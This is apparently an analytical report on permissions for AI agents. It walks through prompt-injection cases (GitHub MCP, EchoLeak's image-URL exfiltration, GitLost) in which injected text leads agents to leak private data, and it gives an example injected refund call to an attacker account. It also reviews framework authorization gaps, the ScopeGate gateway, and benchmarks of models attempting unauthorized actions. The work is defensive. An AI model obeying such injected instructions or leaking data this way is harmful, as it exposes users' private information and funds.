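| Action | Account | Why GitHub allows it |
|---|---|---|
| Open an issue in the Pacman repository | The outsider's | The repository is public |
| Read the issue | The owner's | The repository is public |
| Read the private repositories | The owner's | He owns them |
| Open a pull request in the Pacman repository | The owner's | He owns it |
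| Read the pull request | The outsider's | The repository is public |

Siu and colleagues' condition for a confused deputy also fails to detect the problem, because the user who started the task is allowed to open everything the agent opened. The outsider gained access without having started any task.

What GitHub does not check is the relation between the reading and the writing. Let readers(x) be the set of people who may read x. Copying text from x to y respects the limit on x only if everyone who can read y could already read x:

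readers(y) ⊆ readers(x).

When the model copies text from a private repository that only the owner can open into a pull request in a public repository, readers(x) contains one person and readers(y) contains everybody, so the copy breaks the rule. GitHub can determine both sets, but it receives the pull request as new text, with nothing to show where the model found the contents.

GitHub could not impose this rule on every account without blocking legitimate publishing. Developers regularly publish code that began in a private repository, and the owner of the Pacman game is free to disclose his own salary. His permissions let him publish, and GitHub relies on him to decide when to do so, but once an agent has the same permissions, the model makes that decision.

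EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot that Aim Security disclosed in June 2025, had the same basic form. Copilot searches an employee's mail and files with her permissions. An attacker could send her an email containing hidden instructions, and when she later asked Copilot a question, it might retrieve that email along with confidential documents. The instructions told the model to put confidential text into the web address of an image. Her browser then requested the image, which sent the text to the attacker without her clicking anything. Microsoft fixed the flaw and said it knew of no affected customers. A review of write permissions on documents would probably have missed this route, because the data left in an image request.

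### The identity behind GitLost

In the Pacman case, the owner was at his computer and had asked a question. GitHub Agentic Workflows, which GitHub began previewing in February 2026, can start an agent without a user asking anything. A developer describes a job in ordinary English, and a model carries it out when something happens in the repository, such as someone being assigned an issue.

Levi reported in *GitLost* on 6 July 2026 that this product could leak private files too. Levi leads research at Noma Security, which sells protection for AI agents. The test workflow ran when someone assigned an issue. It read the issue's title and text, then replied in a comment. The issue, which posed as a note from a vice president of sales, asked for a new colour on the login page, the contents of the README in the public repository and, after the word "Additionally", the README from a private repository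 called `testlocal`. The agent answered all three requests in a public comment. The private README contained only a note that the repository was a developer's test, but the agent would presumably have copied a more valuable file in the same way.

The workflow's declared permissions do not explain how the agent reached `testlocal`. MCP Directory's *GitLost*, which examines the files Noma published, reports that they allowed the agent only to read the workflow's own repository. GitHub gives every workflow a token automatically, but it says developers must add a personal access token or an app token for an agent to work across repositories. A personal access token carries some or all of the access of the person who creates it. Developers who commented on Noma's published issue said the researchers had created such a token themselves and given it access to private repositories. MCP Directory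 accepts this explanation, which is consistent with GitHub's documentation.

The agent apparently read the private file with its builder's access, as an agent with maker credentials does in Copilot Studio, except that here the person asking could be a stranger. A Hacker News commenter quoted by MCP Directory concludes that companies should treat whoever writes the issue as the agent's user and give the agent no permission that this person lacks. With that limit, the agent could have read only public repositories, and GitLost would have failed. The Pacman attack would still have worked, because the owner was the user in that case.

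The agent's token was read-only, so the agent proposed a comment and a separate job, with its own permissions, posted it. MCP Directory observes that this job allowed only comments but accepted any content in them. A read-only token would have stopped the agent from damaging `testlocal`, but the leak required only read access and a job that would publish the result.

Some developers objected that Noma had created the weakness it then exploited, which is a good reason not to call GitLost a flaw in GitHub's default settings. But organizations may still create the same weakness themselves, because one token that covers every repository is more convenient than many narrow ones. MCP Directory guesses that some have done so, but nobody in the dispute says how many.

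Noma's emphasis on the word "Additionally" also deserves some caution. Levi writes that GitHub's guardrails failed once the word was included, after repeated attempts with different wordings. Without the number of attempts, readers cannot tell whether the word made the difference or one more attempt happened to succeed.

### What GitHub changed

Four months before Noma's disclosure, GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) warned that a prompt-injected agent could leak secrets through public issues, pull requests and comments. It described defences including a closed container for the agent, a firewall and a gateway that controls access to MCP servers. A firewall does little against GitLost, because the data leaves in a comment that the workflow has permission to post.

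On 17 March GitHub replaced an automatic restriction called lockdown with rules that filter what the agent reads, according to its *Weekly Update* (2026). *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering*, from GitHub's research group, GitHub Next, explains that the filter ranks content by its author and by whether a maintainer has endorsed it. For public repositories the default level is "approved", which covers owners, members and collaborators. An outsider's issue falls below that level, so the filter should remove it before the agent sees it.

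This makes it uncertain how far GitLost applies to a workflow with the default filter. According to MCP Directory, the filter was active in Noma's test, but the published configuration takes the minimum level from a variable whose value isn't shown. The researchers also controlled the repository and assigned the issue themselves. If they opened it from an account that GitHub treated as a collaborator, the filter would have let it through. An organization that depends on this filter should test it with an issue from an outside account.

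The filter also conflicts with one of the main uses of such agents, sorting bug reports from the public. GitHub Next suggests a lower level for that job so that the agent can read issues from contributors, but then an attacker needs only contributor status to get past the filter. A separate setting lets a developer restrict the agent to one repository, or to public ones, even if its token covers more. Either restriction would have kept `testlocal` out of the comment, whatever the issue contained.

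On 11 June, GitHub began letting agentic workflows run with the token it supplies automatically (*Agentic workflows no longer need a personal access token*, 2026). This gives developers one less reason to leave a personal token where an agent can use it. The change would not have helped a workflow like Noma's, because GitHub still tells developers to supply a personal access token if they want the agent to read other repositories.

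All of these changes came before the disclosure. The Next Web's *‘GitLost’* reported that GitHub had not yet documented the problem, and MCP Directory found no code fix when it published. But by 12 July GitHub's developers were adding a setting named `private-to-public-flows` to the product's code, along with a rule that rejects its unrestricted value in strict mode. The setting's name and date suggest a response to GitLost but don't prove it. GitHub Next says in its post that the system labels and tracks data from private repositories but does not yet stop it from reaching the wrong destination, a gap the setting would address.

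### What permissions assume about people

InfoQ's *Indirect Prompt Injection Exploits GitHub's AI Agent to Leak Private Repository Data* (2026) quotes Vijendra Malhotra, a technology executive, who says that a private repository "was never a security boundary" and held only while every reader was a human employee. Malhotra is right that the permission to read the repository assumed a human employee was reading, which GitHub never checked. But "never" goes too far, because the outsider could not open the private repository directly in either GitHub case.

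When a company gives an employee access, it usually makes several unwritten assumptions. She will leave most of the access unused, because opening files takes time and she has other work. If she misuses it, she can do only so much in an afternoon. She will probably notice when a request makes no sense, and she knows she may lose her job over what she does. All of these assumptions sometimes fail, and phishing works because people don't always recognize a strange request. But a company that grants broad access to 500 employees is assuming that such failures will be rare and fairly slow.

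The first and third habits are absent from the Pacman demonstration. The owner could have read all his private repositories at any time, but he had no reason to when he wanted to know about open issues. He would also have found it odd if a stranger had asked for material from those repositories to be published to advertise him.

An agent can do similar damage without an attacker. *AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos* (Markovic, 2026) reports that Glow Labs found more than 13,000 internal images in over 900 public repositories. Developers at more than 300 organizations had asked coding agents to prove that a change to a screen worked. GitHub accepts image uploads for pull requests only through the browser, and the agents worked from the command line, so some posted the images publicly for reviewers to see. At a manufacturer with over 100,000 employees,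 an agent created a public repository in a developer's personal account and filled it with screenshots of a utility company's billing records.

That developer was presumably allowed to see the billing screen and to create a public repository. The agent did not need anyone else's authority, and no one had planted an instruction. Glow Labs reproduced the behaviour with Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, on a copy of Minesweeper. The agent could not attach its screenshots, so it reasoned that they had to be hosted elsewhere and created a new public repository for them.

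The method also spread quickly at a software vendor, where more than a dozen agents saved it as a reusable skill within a week. Together they published more than 1,000 images and recordings, including some of features that the vendor had not yet released. One employee with the same bad idea would probably have posted a few pictures before a colleague objected. Accountability also failed, because 93% of the cases involved repositories under employees' own usernames, so decisions the agents may have made appear under the employees' names.

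Glow Labs' count is stronger evidence than the two demonstrations because it comes from real organizations. But we can't tell from it how often agents make this mistake without knowing how many screenshots they handled properly. Markovic's article also does not explain how Glow Labs distinguished images posted by agents from those posted by people. Developers at about a third of the affected organizations ran gitshot, a tool that publishes screenshots for code reviews and that a person could also run.

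The deletion of PocketOS's production database, which Okta cites in the post about its salary test, is a harder test of the same assumptions. The coding agent found a credential that allowed far more than its task required. Those extra permissions did no harm while the credential sat unused in a file. The agent used it, whereas a developer would probably have wondered what it was for first.

The other habits offer less protection in that case. A person can delete a database almost as quickly as an agent can, so working at human speed would not have limited the damage once the deletion began. As far as is known, no outsider had planted a request that an employee might have found suspicious. Fear of the consequences might have stopped an employee, but a company can only hold people responsible after the database is gone.

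PocketOS also shows why it is hard to say how much access an agent has. An agent that can read a developer's files can use any working credential stored in them, so it can do everything those credentials allow, even if no administrator granted it that access. A company that wants the agent to have less access than the developer therefore has to keep it away from her stored credentials as well as reduce the permissions on the agent's own account.

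### All of the user's access, or less

There are reasonable arguments for giving an agent all of its user's access. Many useful tasks involve several repositories, and users and administrators cannot always predict which ones. Invariant Labs recommends narrow access but concedes that limits on access tokens are often rigid and make agents less useful. Restrictions can also backfire. The agents that Glow Labs studied published screenshots because they could not attach them in the ordinary way. And if an employee is allowed to read and publish something herself, a company may see little point in stopping an agent from doing so at her request.

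That last argument is the weakest, because it assumes that the user requested everything the agent does under her account. The owner of the Pacman game asked to see his open issues. GitHub's records would show that his account then published his salary, but he had not chosen to publish it. The argument from usefulness is better, and it is a reason not to cut permissions at random. But an agent can have broad access without leaking anything if that access leaves no route from private data to the public.

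Levi makes a related point in *GitLost Flaw Lets Attackers Trick GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking Private Repos*, tracing the problem to a mismatch between where an agent gets its permissions and where it gets its input. In GitLost the permissions came from someone inside the organization and the input from a public form. Few jobs need both of these along with the ability to publish. The owner of the Pacman game could divide his work like this:

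| Task | Outsiders' text | Private repositories | Public writing |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sort and label new issues | Yes | No | Yes |
| Improve private code | No | Yes | No |
| Answer a bug report with help from private code | Yes | Yes | Only after he approves the text |

An agent with all of the owner's access has a "yes" in every cell, whatever the task. When the access is divided, an outsider can still trick the sorting agent into posting nonsense, but that agent can't reveal a salary because it can't read one. Only the third task needs the owner's attention. He reads one finished reply, which is easier than judging each tool call as it appears, though he could still miss a private detail in a long reply.

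Invariant Labs proposes a stricter rule, enforced by its own product, that limits an agent to one repository per session. The rule would have blocked the Pacman attack when the agent moved from the public repository to a private one, but it would also block legitimate changes that involve two repositories. And because the rule is applied to MCP tool calls, an agent that posts to GitHub from the command line, as those in Glow Labs' investigation did, could bypass it.

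If *Why You (Probably) Should Not Give Your Agent GitHub Access* is right, GitHub's credentials alone can't produce the divided arrangement. According to the article, an app's credential can limit access to private repositories but not to public ones, so the agent could send stolen text to any public repository. A personal access token may also let the agent create a new public repository, as the agent at the manufacturer did. For the agent that improves private code, the owner would therefore need a control outside GitHub's permissions, such as a tool that can write to one named repository and has no command for creating others.

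The case for less access is strong for agents that read text from strangers, and the lost convenience seems modest. The case is also fairly strong for coding agents that work unattended, since the problems Glow Labs found did not depend on text from strangers. Full access is easier to defend for an agent that reads only trusted material, cannot publish, and works while its user watches. Using separate agents provides little protection if they share memory or a working folder. For example, the agent that sorts issues could find the owner's salary in a note left there by the agent that reads his private repositories.

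## Tool access without a check on each call: three agent frameworks

Developers usually decide which tools an agent has before anyone uses the agent, but the model fills in the arguments each time it calls a tool. An agent that may issue refunds can therefore send one to the wrong account unless something checks each call. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) found no such check among the defaults of three common agent frameworks.

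### A valid refund to the wrong account

Suppose an online shop's support agent has a tool called `issue_refund`, which takes an amount and a destination account. A customer's message contains an injected instruction, and the model makes this call:

```
issue_refund(amount=40, account="acct_ATTACKER_999")
```

| Check | Question | Answer |
|---|---|---|
| Tool list | Does the agent have a tool called `issue_refund`? | Yes |
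| Schema | Is the amount a number and the account a piece of text? | Yes |
| Per-call authorization | May the agent send this refund to this account? | No |

If the software runs only the first two checks, the shop pays the attacker. The schema, which describes the form each argument must have, would reject an amount of "forty", but it contains nothing about who owns an account.

Mellafe Zuvic calls the choice of tools "capability gating". The name is a little confusing, because a capability in Hardy's sense covers one object, whereas this tool works on any account the model names. The shop's permission doesn't specify an account, so the model chooses one after reading the attacker's text.

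The same gap exists for amounts. Auth0's *Why AI Agents Need Their Own Permission Model* (2026) describes a hypothetical support agent that is supposed to make small goodwill refunds but holds the scope `billing:write`, because the billing system offers nothing narrower. When a user asks for a full refund on a $10,000 order, the agent issues it. Auth0 belongs to Okta and sells authorization software, but the example doesn't depend on survey data.

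The shop could avoid part of the problem by having `issue_refund` take only an order number and return the money to the card used for the purchase. The model would then not choose where the money goes. It could still submit another customer's order number, so the tool's code would also have to check that the order belongs to the customer in the conversation.

### What the frameworks check

Mellafe Zuvic, an independent researcher in Chile, read the public source code of LangChain and its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit. LangChain and LlamaIndex are general frameworks for building agents, and Stripe's toolkit connects agents to its payment service. He looked for a check that runs after the model makes a call and before the tool acts, examines the actual values in the call, and always gives the same answer to the same call. The check also had to be "fail-closed",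 meaning it refuses a call when no rule allows it or when the check itself breaks.

| Software | What it checks by default | What it leaves to the developer |
|---|---|---|
| LangChain and LangGraph | The tool exists and, in common cases, the arguments have the right form | Rules about values, and human approval |
| LlamaIndex | The tool exists | Rules about values, and human approval, which the tool's author must write into the tool |
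| Stripe Agent Toolkit | The action is on a fixed list, and the API key allows that kind of operation | Rules about the amount, customer or payment |

When a model calls a tool that doesn't exist, LlamaIndex returns a "not found" message to the model but raises no security alert. LangChain lets developers attach callbacks, functions that run when a tool is used. Mellafe Zuvic found that these callbacks observe calls but cannot reliably block them.

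The stakes are highest with the Stripe toolkit because it handles money. Stripe's *Restricted API keys* warns that anyone with an account's ordinary secret key, including an agent, can do anything in the account. Stripe strongly recommends a restricted key for the toolkit, and the permissions on that key determine which tools the agent gets. A key without refund permission prevents every refund, but if the key allows refunds, the toolkit passes on whatever amount and payment the model supplies. Stripe also runs a remote MCP server, which may apply further checks that Mellafe Zuvic could not inspect.

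LangChain's *Human-in-the-Loop* describes a component that developers can add to pause an agent for human approval when it calls a tool on a list. By November 2026, they could also attach a function that checks the call's arguments, so that only refunds above $50, for example, wait for a person. This is a check on each call, but it differs from the one Mellafe Zuvic looked for. The function can only pause a call or let it through, and tools missing from the list run without review.

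The function also runs again when the agent resumes. If its result is now that the call needs no review, LangChain runs the tool regardless of the reviewer's answer, even if it was a rejection. Under a rule such as "pause once today's refunds exceed $500", the shop may pay a refund that an employee has refused if the total resets at midnight while the refund is waiting.

To show the gap was real, Mellafe Zuvic gave LangChain a fixed model output that called for changing a merchant's payout account to `acct_ATTACKER_999`. LangChain's ordinary code made the change on a simulated payment system, and a companion test with LlamaIndex gave the same result. He describes the three frameworks' designs as leaving the check on each call to the developer, and doesn't claim to have found a vulnerability in any of them.

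That design is defensible because a framework's makers can't know which accounts a shop trusts. But they could have the framework refuse every call to a tool that changes something until the developer writes a rule, much as Postgres hides all rows when a table has row-level security and no policy. This would make the first hour more annoying for new developers, and some would just write "allow everything". For tools that move money, it still seems worth it. The audit doesn't show how many working agents lack a check, because developers may have added their own or put one in the tool's code.

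### How often models attempt unauthorized calls

The missing check would matter less if models almost never attempted unauthorized calls. Mellafe Zuvic summarizes his companion benchmark, in which 27 models read injected "task-aligned" instructions, which presented the forbidden action as a step the user's task required. His attempt rate is the share of trials in which a model made an unauthorized call or reproduced a planted marker that served as evidence of one. All trials ran in a sandbox that blocked real effects, so the rates measure attempts, not breaches.

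| Group | Models | Mean attempt rate | Examples |
|---|---|---|---|
| Low-cost models | 12 | 0.603 | gpt-4o-mini 1.000, gemini-3.1-flash-lite 0.980 |
| Flagship models | 15 | 0.189 | glm-5.2 0.087, gemini-3.1-pro-preview 0.000 |

The low-cost models attempted unauthorized actions about three times as often on average, but Mellafe Zuvic gives no confidence interval for the difference, and both groups include models with high rates. He argues that companies are likely to use low-cost models for high-volume work, but he infers this from their price and has no data on which models companies use.

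Separate tests suggest that the wording of injected text strongly affects whether a model attempts a forbidden action. glm-4.7 attempted the action in 28% of trials with crude text and in all trials with task-aligned text. For mistral-large, the rate rose from 3% to 46%. But for Latam-GPT, a version of Meta's Llama model adapted for Latin America, the rate in Spanish fell from 24% to 4%. The same model attempted an unauthorized payout in all 10 trials of a Spanish payment scenario built for a different test. A company that saw only the 4% rate could easily have concluded that the model was safe for payments.

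Other researchers have also found frequent overreach in larger tests. AuthorizationBench, from *Act on Your Behalf, Beyond Your Authorization* (2026), gives agents tasks based on documented cases and records whether they stay within what the user authorized. Agents exceeded their authorization in 19.2% of 6,864 runs. The rate was 14.0% when agents consulted the user before finishing and 21.6% when they did not, although agents may have consulted users more often on tasks where the limits were obvious.

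*Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026) recommends that evaluations examine the unauthorized effects an agent could still cause as well as those it caused. By that standard, an agent running gemini-3.1-pro-preview on LangChain's defaults remains exposed. The model made no forbidden calls in the benchmark, but if a cleverer message leads it to make one, the framework will execute the call.

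### ScopeGate's five stages

Mellafe Zuvic's remedy is ScopeGate, a program that sits between the model and the tools and uses no language model. An operator, meaning whoever runs the agent, writes a policy in advance and keeps it where the model can't read or change it. For each call, ScopeGate goes through five stages:

1. **Scope.** It refuses any tool that the policy doesn't list.
2. **Authorization.** For each argument that the policy restricts, it refuses values outside an allowlist. If the only approved account is `acct_MERCHANT_001`, it refuses `acct_ATTACKER_999` here.
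3. **Money ceiling.** It refuses an amount that is negative, above the limit or not an ordinary number.
4. **Idempotency.** For tools that need one, it requires an idempotency key, a unique label that lets a payment system recognize a repeated request and avoid paying twice.
5. **Default deny.** It allows the call only if all the earlier stages passed, and refuses it if an error occurs.

The model must not be able to change the policy. Otherwise, an injection that can change the account in a call could also add that account to the allowlist.

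| Test | Unauthorized calls | Refused | Legitimate calls | Allowed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Fixed bypass attempts | 48 | 48 | None | |
| Attacker that adapts over 40 rounds | 29 | 29 | 2 | 2 |
| Legitimate requests to two low-cost models | None | | 10 | 10 |
| Latam-GPT payment agent | 10 | 10 | None | |

The fixed attempts included misspelled tool names, invisible characters and look-alike letters. The adaptive attacker was the language model GLM-5.2, which received the reason for each refusal before it tried again. Nine of its 40 calls were too malformed to count.

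The fixed attempts also exposed a bug in an earlier version of ScopeGate. NaN ("not a number") is a special value that computers use for the results of impossible calculations, and any comparison with it is false. The early code refused an amount if it was greater than the ceiling, so NaN passed. The current code requires a finite number between zero and the ceiling, so it refuses NaN. The bug is a good argument for writing such rules as conditions for approval instead of refusal.

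These results show that ScopeGate works as described on the calls that Mellafe Zuvic tried. He designed the program, wrote the fixed attacks and used simulated payments, and he says that the zeroes don't prove a bypass is impossible. The figure for false refusals is the weakest. Even if the ten legitimate requests were a random sample of real work, zero false refusals would be compatible, at 95% confidence, with a true rate of up to about 26%.

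The published algorithm also has limitations that none of these tests would reveal. It checks only the arguments that the policy restricts, so if the operator forgets to restrict one, such as the web address a customer goes to after paying, the model can fill in anything. It checks arguments one at a time, so it would allow a refund for Ana's order to go to Ben's account if both accounts are on the list. It also applies the ceiling to each call separately, so with a ceiling of $50, an agent could still pay out $10,000 in 200 refunds, as long as each has an idempotency key.

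Other designs address some of these gaps. Auth0 describes a rule that lets an agent refund an order only if it belongs to a customer whose support ticket the agent is handling. This rule connects two facts that ScopeGate would check separately. *AgentCap* (2026) presents a gateway that issues a signed permit for each call and can limit the total budget as well as the action and resource. Its tests are also broader, using two public benchmarks, AgentDojo and InjecAgent. The gateway reduced successful attacks for every model tested. With GPT-5.4, no attacks succeeded on either benchmark.

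A list of approved values doesn't help much when an argument is free text. An operator can't list every acceptable query for Supabase's `execute_sql` in advance, and in GitLost the private data was in the text of a permitted comment. Per-call authorization works best with narrow tools whose arguments are accounts, amounts and record numbers.

### Whose rights the policy contains

Mellafe Zuvic's definition of per-call authorization includes the "principal", the party for whom the call runs, but ScopeGate's algorithm never reads it. The program reads only the idempotency key from the trusted context it receives with each call. Everything else comes from the operator's policy, which is the same for every requesting user.

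These checks can still let the payroll company's shared agent disclose one employee's pay record to another. Suppose the agent has a tool that returns the pay record for a given employee number. Because the agent serves the payroll clerk, the operator's allowlist has to contain all 500 numbers. If employee 17 asks for employee 203's record, ScopeGate allows the call because the tool is on the list, 203 is an approved value, no money moves, and a read needs no idempotency key. The agent is then a confused deputy even though ScopeGate checked every argument.

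The company could fix this by choosing the policy based on who has logged in. Employee 17's allowlist would contain only 17, and the clerk's would contain all 500 numbers. This seems compatible with Mellafe Zuvic's conditions, as long as the user's identity comes from the login and never from the model. He doesn't test it, though. He also requires the policy to stay fixed for the whole conversation, so a clerk who lost her payroll access at noon could keep reading records in a conversation she began that morning.

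In Auth0's refund example, the authorization engine OpenFGA stores a rule that the agent may refund up to $50 on a certain order. When the agent attempts $75, the engine refuses, and Auth0 suggests asking a person to approve the refund. The stored limit takes precedence over anything in the request, so a misled model can't raise it. But the field named `user` in Auth0's code contains `agent:support_agent_01`, so the $50 limit belongs to the agent, regardless of who is asking.

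An operator's allowlist may suit tasks like refunds, where the agent needs authority that the customer lacks, as with Ritchie's accounting program. Customers have no permission to issue refunds, so an agent limited to a customer's rights couldn't issue one either. However, something must also check that the order belongs to the customer.

### Letting a model decide

Because writing policies takes work, some companies would prefer to describe their rules in ordinary English and have a second model judge each request. AuthZed's *Agent authorization* reports a test in which a model received the request "The executive assistant is requesting permission to purchase a flight to Las Vegas." In one run, the model refused because the request didn't say the flight was for the chief executive. In the next run, with the same model, prompt and request, it approved because booking travel was among the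 assistant's permissions.

This is an anecdote from AuthZed, a vendor that sells a conventional authorization system. AuthZed doesn't name the model or say how many times it ran the test, and it admits that its policy was under-specified. With conventional software, someone would have had to decide whether a request must name the traveller. The software would then have given the same answer each time, though that answer might be wrong.

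*Same Operation, Different Permission* (Jing, Chen and colleagues, 2026) provides better evidence that answers vary. The researchers gave models the same operation with valid and invalid permission, such as a refund under an active delegation and the same refund after someone had revoked the delegation. In three runs that differed only in random seed, a small model, Qwen3.5-9B, approved 3, 0 and 14 of 80 forbidden operations.

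They also tested three models on 1,215 requests written for OpenFGA and Cedar, two conventional authorization engines.

| Judge | Forbidden requests approved (of 448) | Permitted requests approved (of 767) |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.5-9B | 261 | 656 |
| Qwen3.5-27B | 1 | 757 |
| GPT-OSS Safeguard | 12 | 588 |
| Qwen3.5-27B, then Safeguard | 0 | 586 |

Qwen3.5-27B was right 99.1% of the time, far better than one would expect from AuthZed's anecdote. Its one wrong approval let a user open a folder because he owned a document inside it. The requests come from public examples, so some may have been in the models' training data. More importantly, Jing and colleagues took the correct answers from the engines. A company whose rules are already written for such an engine can run it and get all 1,215 right, so it has little reason to ask a model.

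Database queries are harder for models. Fei, Jiang and colleagues (2026), in *Benchmarking Text-to-SQL under Role-Based Access Control*, gave 13 models questions, each with a user's role and a list of the columns and operations that role may use. The models had to write a permitted query or refuse. GPT-5 broke the rules in 2.6% of cases on Spider, a collection of fairly small databases, and in 17.8% on LiveSQLBench, whose databases have about four times as many columns on average. Claude Sonnet 4.5 broke them in 4.9% of cases on Spider and 13.3% on LiveSQLBench. These models date from 2025, and newer ones may do better.

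The rates overstate how much data would leak, because Fei and colleagues also count a violation when a model should have refused but wrote a query that used only permitted columns. On a third collection, BIRD, about 126 of GPT-5-mini's 194 violations per run were of this kind. Nearly all the rest used forbidden columns that existed in the database. When the researchers removed those columns from the description the model received, it guessed their names and used them 144 times, compared with 69 when they were listed. Evidently the database still needs to refuse forbidden queries even when the forbidden parts are hidden from the model, and Fei and colleagues say that enforcement should stay in the database.

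Models are more useful where no written rule exists. *Can LLMs Make (Personalized) Access Control Decisions?* (2025), from ETH Zurich, tested models on smartphone permission decisions, such as whether an app may use the user's location. The models agreed with the majority of users in up to 86% of cases. That level of agreement may be good enough for suggesting a phone setting, but it is too low for controlling access to salary records. When the models also followed an individual's stated preferences, their decisions matched that person's more closely but were sometimes less safe, because people tend to grant apps too much access.

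A company could combine the two methods by letting a model veto calls that a conventional check has already allowed. A misled model then can't allow a call that the check has refused, and it may catch a permitted call that has nothing to do with the task. However, in the last row of the table from Jing and colleagues, adding Safeguard as a second judge removed one wrong approval but blocked 171 permitted requests. People who meet that many refusals will probably look for a way to turn the judge off.

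AuthZed suggests using a model to write the rules and a conventional engine to enforce them. But Mellafe Zuvic forbids any part of a policy to come from a model, even one that works offline before the agent starts. His ban protects against a tampered-with model, but it seems too strict if a person reads the rules before they take effect. A model that drafts rules from the company's handbook isn't exposed to the attacker's message, and an allowlist is short enough for an administrator to check.

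## Agents that query data as the person asking: Cloudflare, Databricks and PAR

An allowlist can cover refund accounts but not free-form database queries, so an agent that writes its own SQL needs limits in the database or in code around it. Cloudflare, Databricks and PAR Technology have each described a way to return different rows to two people who ask the same question, without trusting the model to choose the rows. Two of these designs have gaps that their makers leave out of their security claims. None of the three protects the rows once they have been copied.

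### Caller's rights and owner's rights

The question of whose permissions apply came up in databases long before it came up with agents, because many people may run the same stored procedure, a small program kept in the database. Snowflake, a cloud data warehouse, has two kinds of stored procedure, according to its *Understanding caller's rights and owner's rights stored procedures*. A procedure with caller's rights can do only what the person running it could do directly, while one with owner's rights uses the permissions of the role that owns it.

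In Snowflake's example, the Doctor role can delete rows from a table of medical records, but the Nurse role can't. A doctor writes an owner's-rights procedure that deletes only rows past a certain age, then lets nurses run it. Nurses can then delete old rows but not recent ones. With caller's rights, the procedure would fail when a nurse ran it.

Owner's rights are safe here, as Ritchie's accounting program was, because someone decided what the procedure would do before anyone ran it. They would be a terrible choice for a procedure that ran whatever SQL a model wrote. Snowflake uses owner's rights by default. Oracle, which calls the two options definer's and invoker's rights, also defaults to the owner's permissions, but only for backward compatibility. It prefers the caller's permissions, according to its *Invoker's Rights and Definer's Rights (AUTHID Property)*.

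A single query can use more than one user's permissions. In its Azure Databricks documentation, Microsoft distinguishes the session user, who sent the query, from the authorized user, whose permissions the database is checking at that moment. When a query reads a view, the view's owner becomes the authorized user until the view has finished. An agent connected as an employee who has no permission for the payroll table can therefore still read the whole table through a view that someone else owns.

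The session user stays the same throughout, so the view's owner can prevent this by having the view return only rows that match `session_user()`. The view still reads the table with the owner's permission, but the employee sees only rows that match their name. Developers who copy such a filter from another database should check it, because `current_user` means the session user in Azure Databricks but the authorized user in standard SQL.

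Snowflake also has a narrower option that is close to delegation. According to its *Restricted caller’s rights*, a program gets only the caller's privileges that an administrator has approved. A company can limit an agent's session in a similar way, according to Snowflake's *Agent identity*.

### Where the identity enters

Suppose the owner of two restaurants in a large chain asks an agent for last week's sales.

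1. She logs in, and the application receives a token or session that identifies her.
2. She types her question. The application puts the question in the model's context and keeps the token out of it.
3. The model reads a description of the tables and writes `SELECT SUM(revenue) FROM weekly_sales`.
4. Ordinary code takes this text and attaches her identity, either by connecting to the database as her or by adding conditions to the query.
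5. The database applies the limits and returns a result.
6. The model reads the result and writes an answer.

The limits from step 4 apply whatever the model writes at step 3, even if it requests another owner's restaurants. If the query tool instead had a `user_id` argument for the model to fill in, the restaurant owner could ask it to enter someone else's ID. An injected instruction could tell it to do the same without her knowing.

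PAR Technology makes software for restaurants. According to its *Multi-tenant LLM analytics with row-level security*, the team's first instinct was to put the user's business ID in the prompt and tell the model to filter by it. They rejected the idea because a model might apply the filter ten thousand times and then omit it. That number is an illustration, since PAR reports no measured failure rate, but the reasoning is sound.

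As in Copilot Studio, the code at step 4 may still connect as someone other than the logged-in user. *Identity and permissions*, from the data catalogue vendor Alation, lists the credential used to run the query as a separate factor from the user's role and grants. Microsoft's Fabric data platform lets customers run the same SQL endpoint in two modes. In one, the endpoint passes the signed-in user's identity to the storage layer, and in the other it connects as the owner of the workspace or item and relies on rules defined in SQL.

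### Skipper runs as the employee

Cloudflare, which runs a large network for websites, described its internal data agent, Skipper, in May 2026. The company had put its scattered data behind one SQL interface, Town Lake, and built Skipper to answer employees' questions in plain English. Cloudflare says everything Skipper does "runs as the calling user".

The query engine, Trino, enforces the limits. A service called Lifeguard stores the access rules, fetches each employee's group membership from the company's access system and produces a policy that Trino reads. The same policy applies whether an employee or Skipper wrote the query.

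This suits Skipper's unusual tool design. Its MCP server offers two tools instead of about 30, one for searching and one that runs JavaScript written by the model. A script can send many queries, and a gateway that checked only the tool call's arguments would have just a block of code to inspect. Trino checks each query regardless of its source. In Cloudflare's sample script, the function that starts a query takes the SQL and no user name, as it should, although the company doesn't explain how the user's identity gets from the login to Trino.

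When someone adds a table to Town Lake, a scanner looks for personal information, and employees can't query the table until a reviewer approves it and its columns. Trino redacts sensitive columns by default. An employee who needs the real values, such as for a fraud investigation, can lift the redaction for a session if her permissions allow it, and Cloudflare logs this. It is unclear whether Skipper can lift the redaction for her. If it can, an injected instruction could make it do so, so requiring a click from the employee would be safer.

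Cloudflare has not published a test in which someone tries to get around these rules. It does report that in one measurement period, 324 employees ran 91,760 queries about billing, 53% of Town Lake's total. That is decent evidence that people can work under user-scoped access, which companies often fear will make an agent useless.

### The token Databricks forwards

Databricks sells a data platform to other companies, so its customers have to build the link between user and query themselves. Databricks says its permission system, Unity Catalog, can use row filters to hide rows from a user and column masks to hide or alter the values in a column.

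An agent built as a Databricks app can use either of two identities, according to Databricks' *Authentication for agents*. The default is the app's own service principal (Databricks' term for a service account), whose permissions all users share. The alternative is user authorization, formerly called "on-behalf-of" access. Databricks restricts the user's credentials to scopes the developer has declared and forwards the resulting token to the app in a request header. When the agent's code connects with that token, Unity Catalog applies the user's filters and masks.

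If the forwarded token is missing, the function that should connect as the user connects as the service principal instead and raises no error. Databricks warns that the agent can then give "a normal-looking response while still acting as the app". This can happen when nobody has enabled the feature, the app has no scopes, or the code connects at startup, before any user has sent a request.

Databricks' sales material is less careful. According to *How do I build custom agents that use company data securely?*, an agent with on-behalf-of access "can never see more than the user can". *How do I build apps that respect my existing data permissions* adds that an app "cannot bypass governance no matter which API it calls". The first claim is true of a request that carries the user's token but can be false after a fallback. The second is still technically true after a fallback, because Unity Catalog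 checks permissions, but it checks the service principal's instead of the user's. Supabase's statement that its row policies remained fully enforced is true in much the same way.

A fallback can expose any data the service principal may read. Databricks suggests that an agent can use both identities, for example the service principal's for a shared search index and the user's for tables that differ by user. A developer who follows this advice should give the service principal no access to those tables, so that a query that falls back to it will fail and someone will notice.

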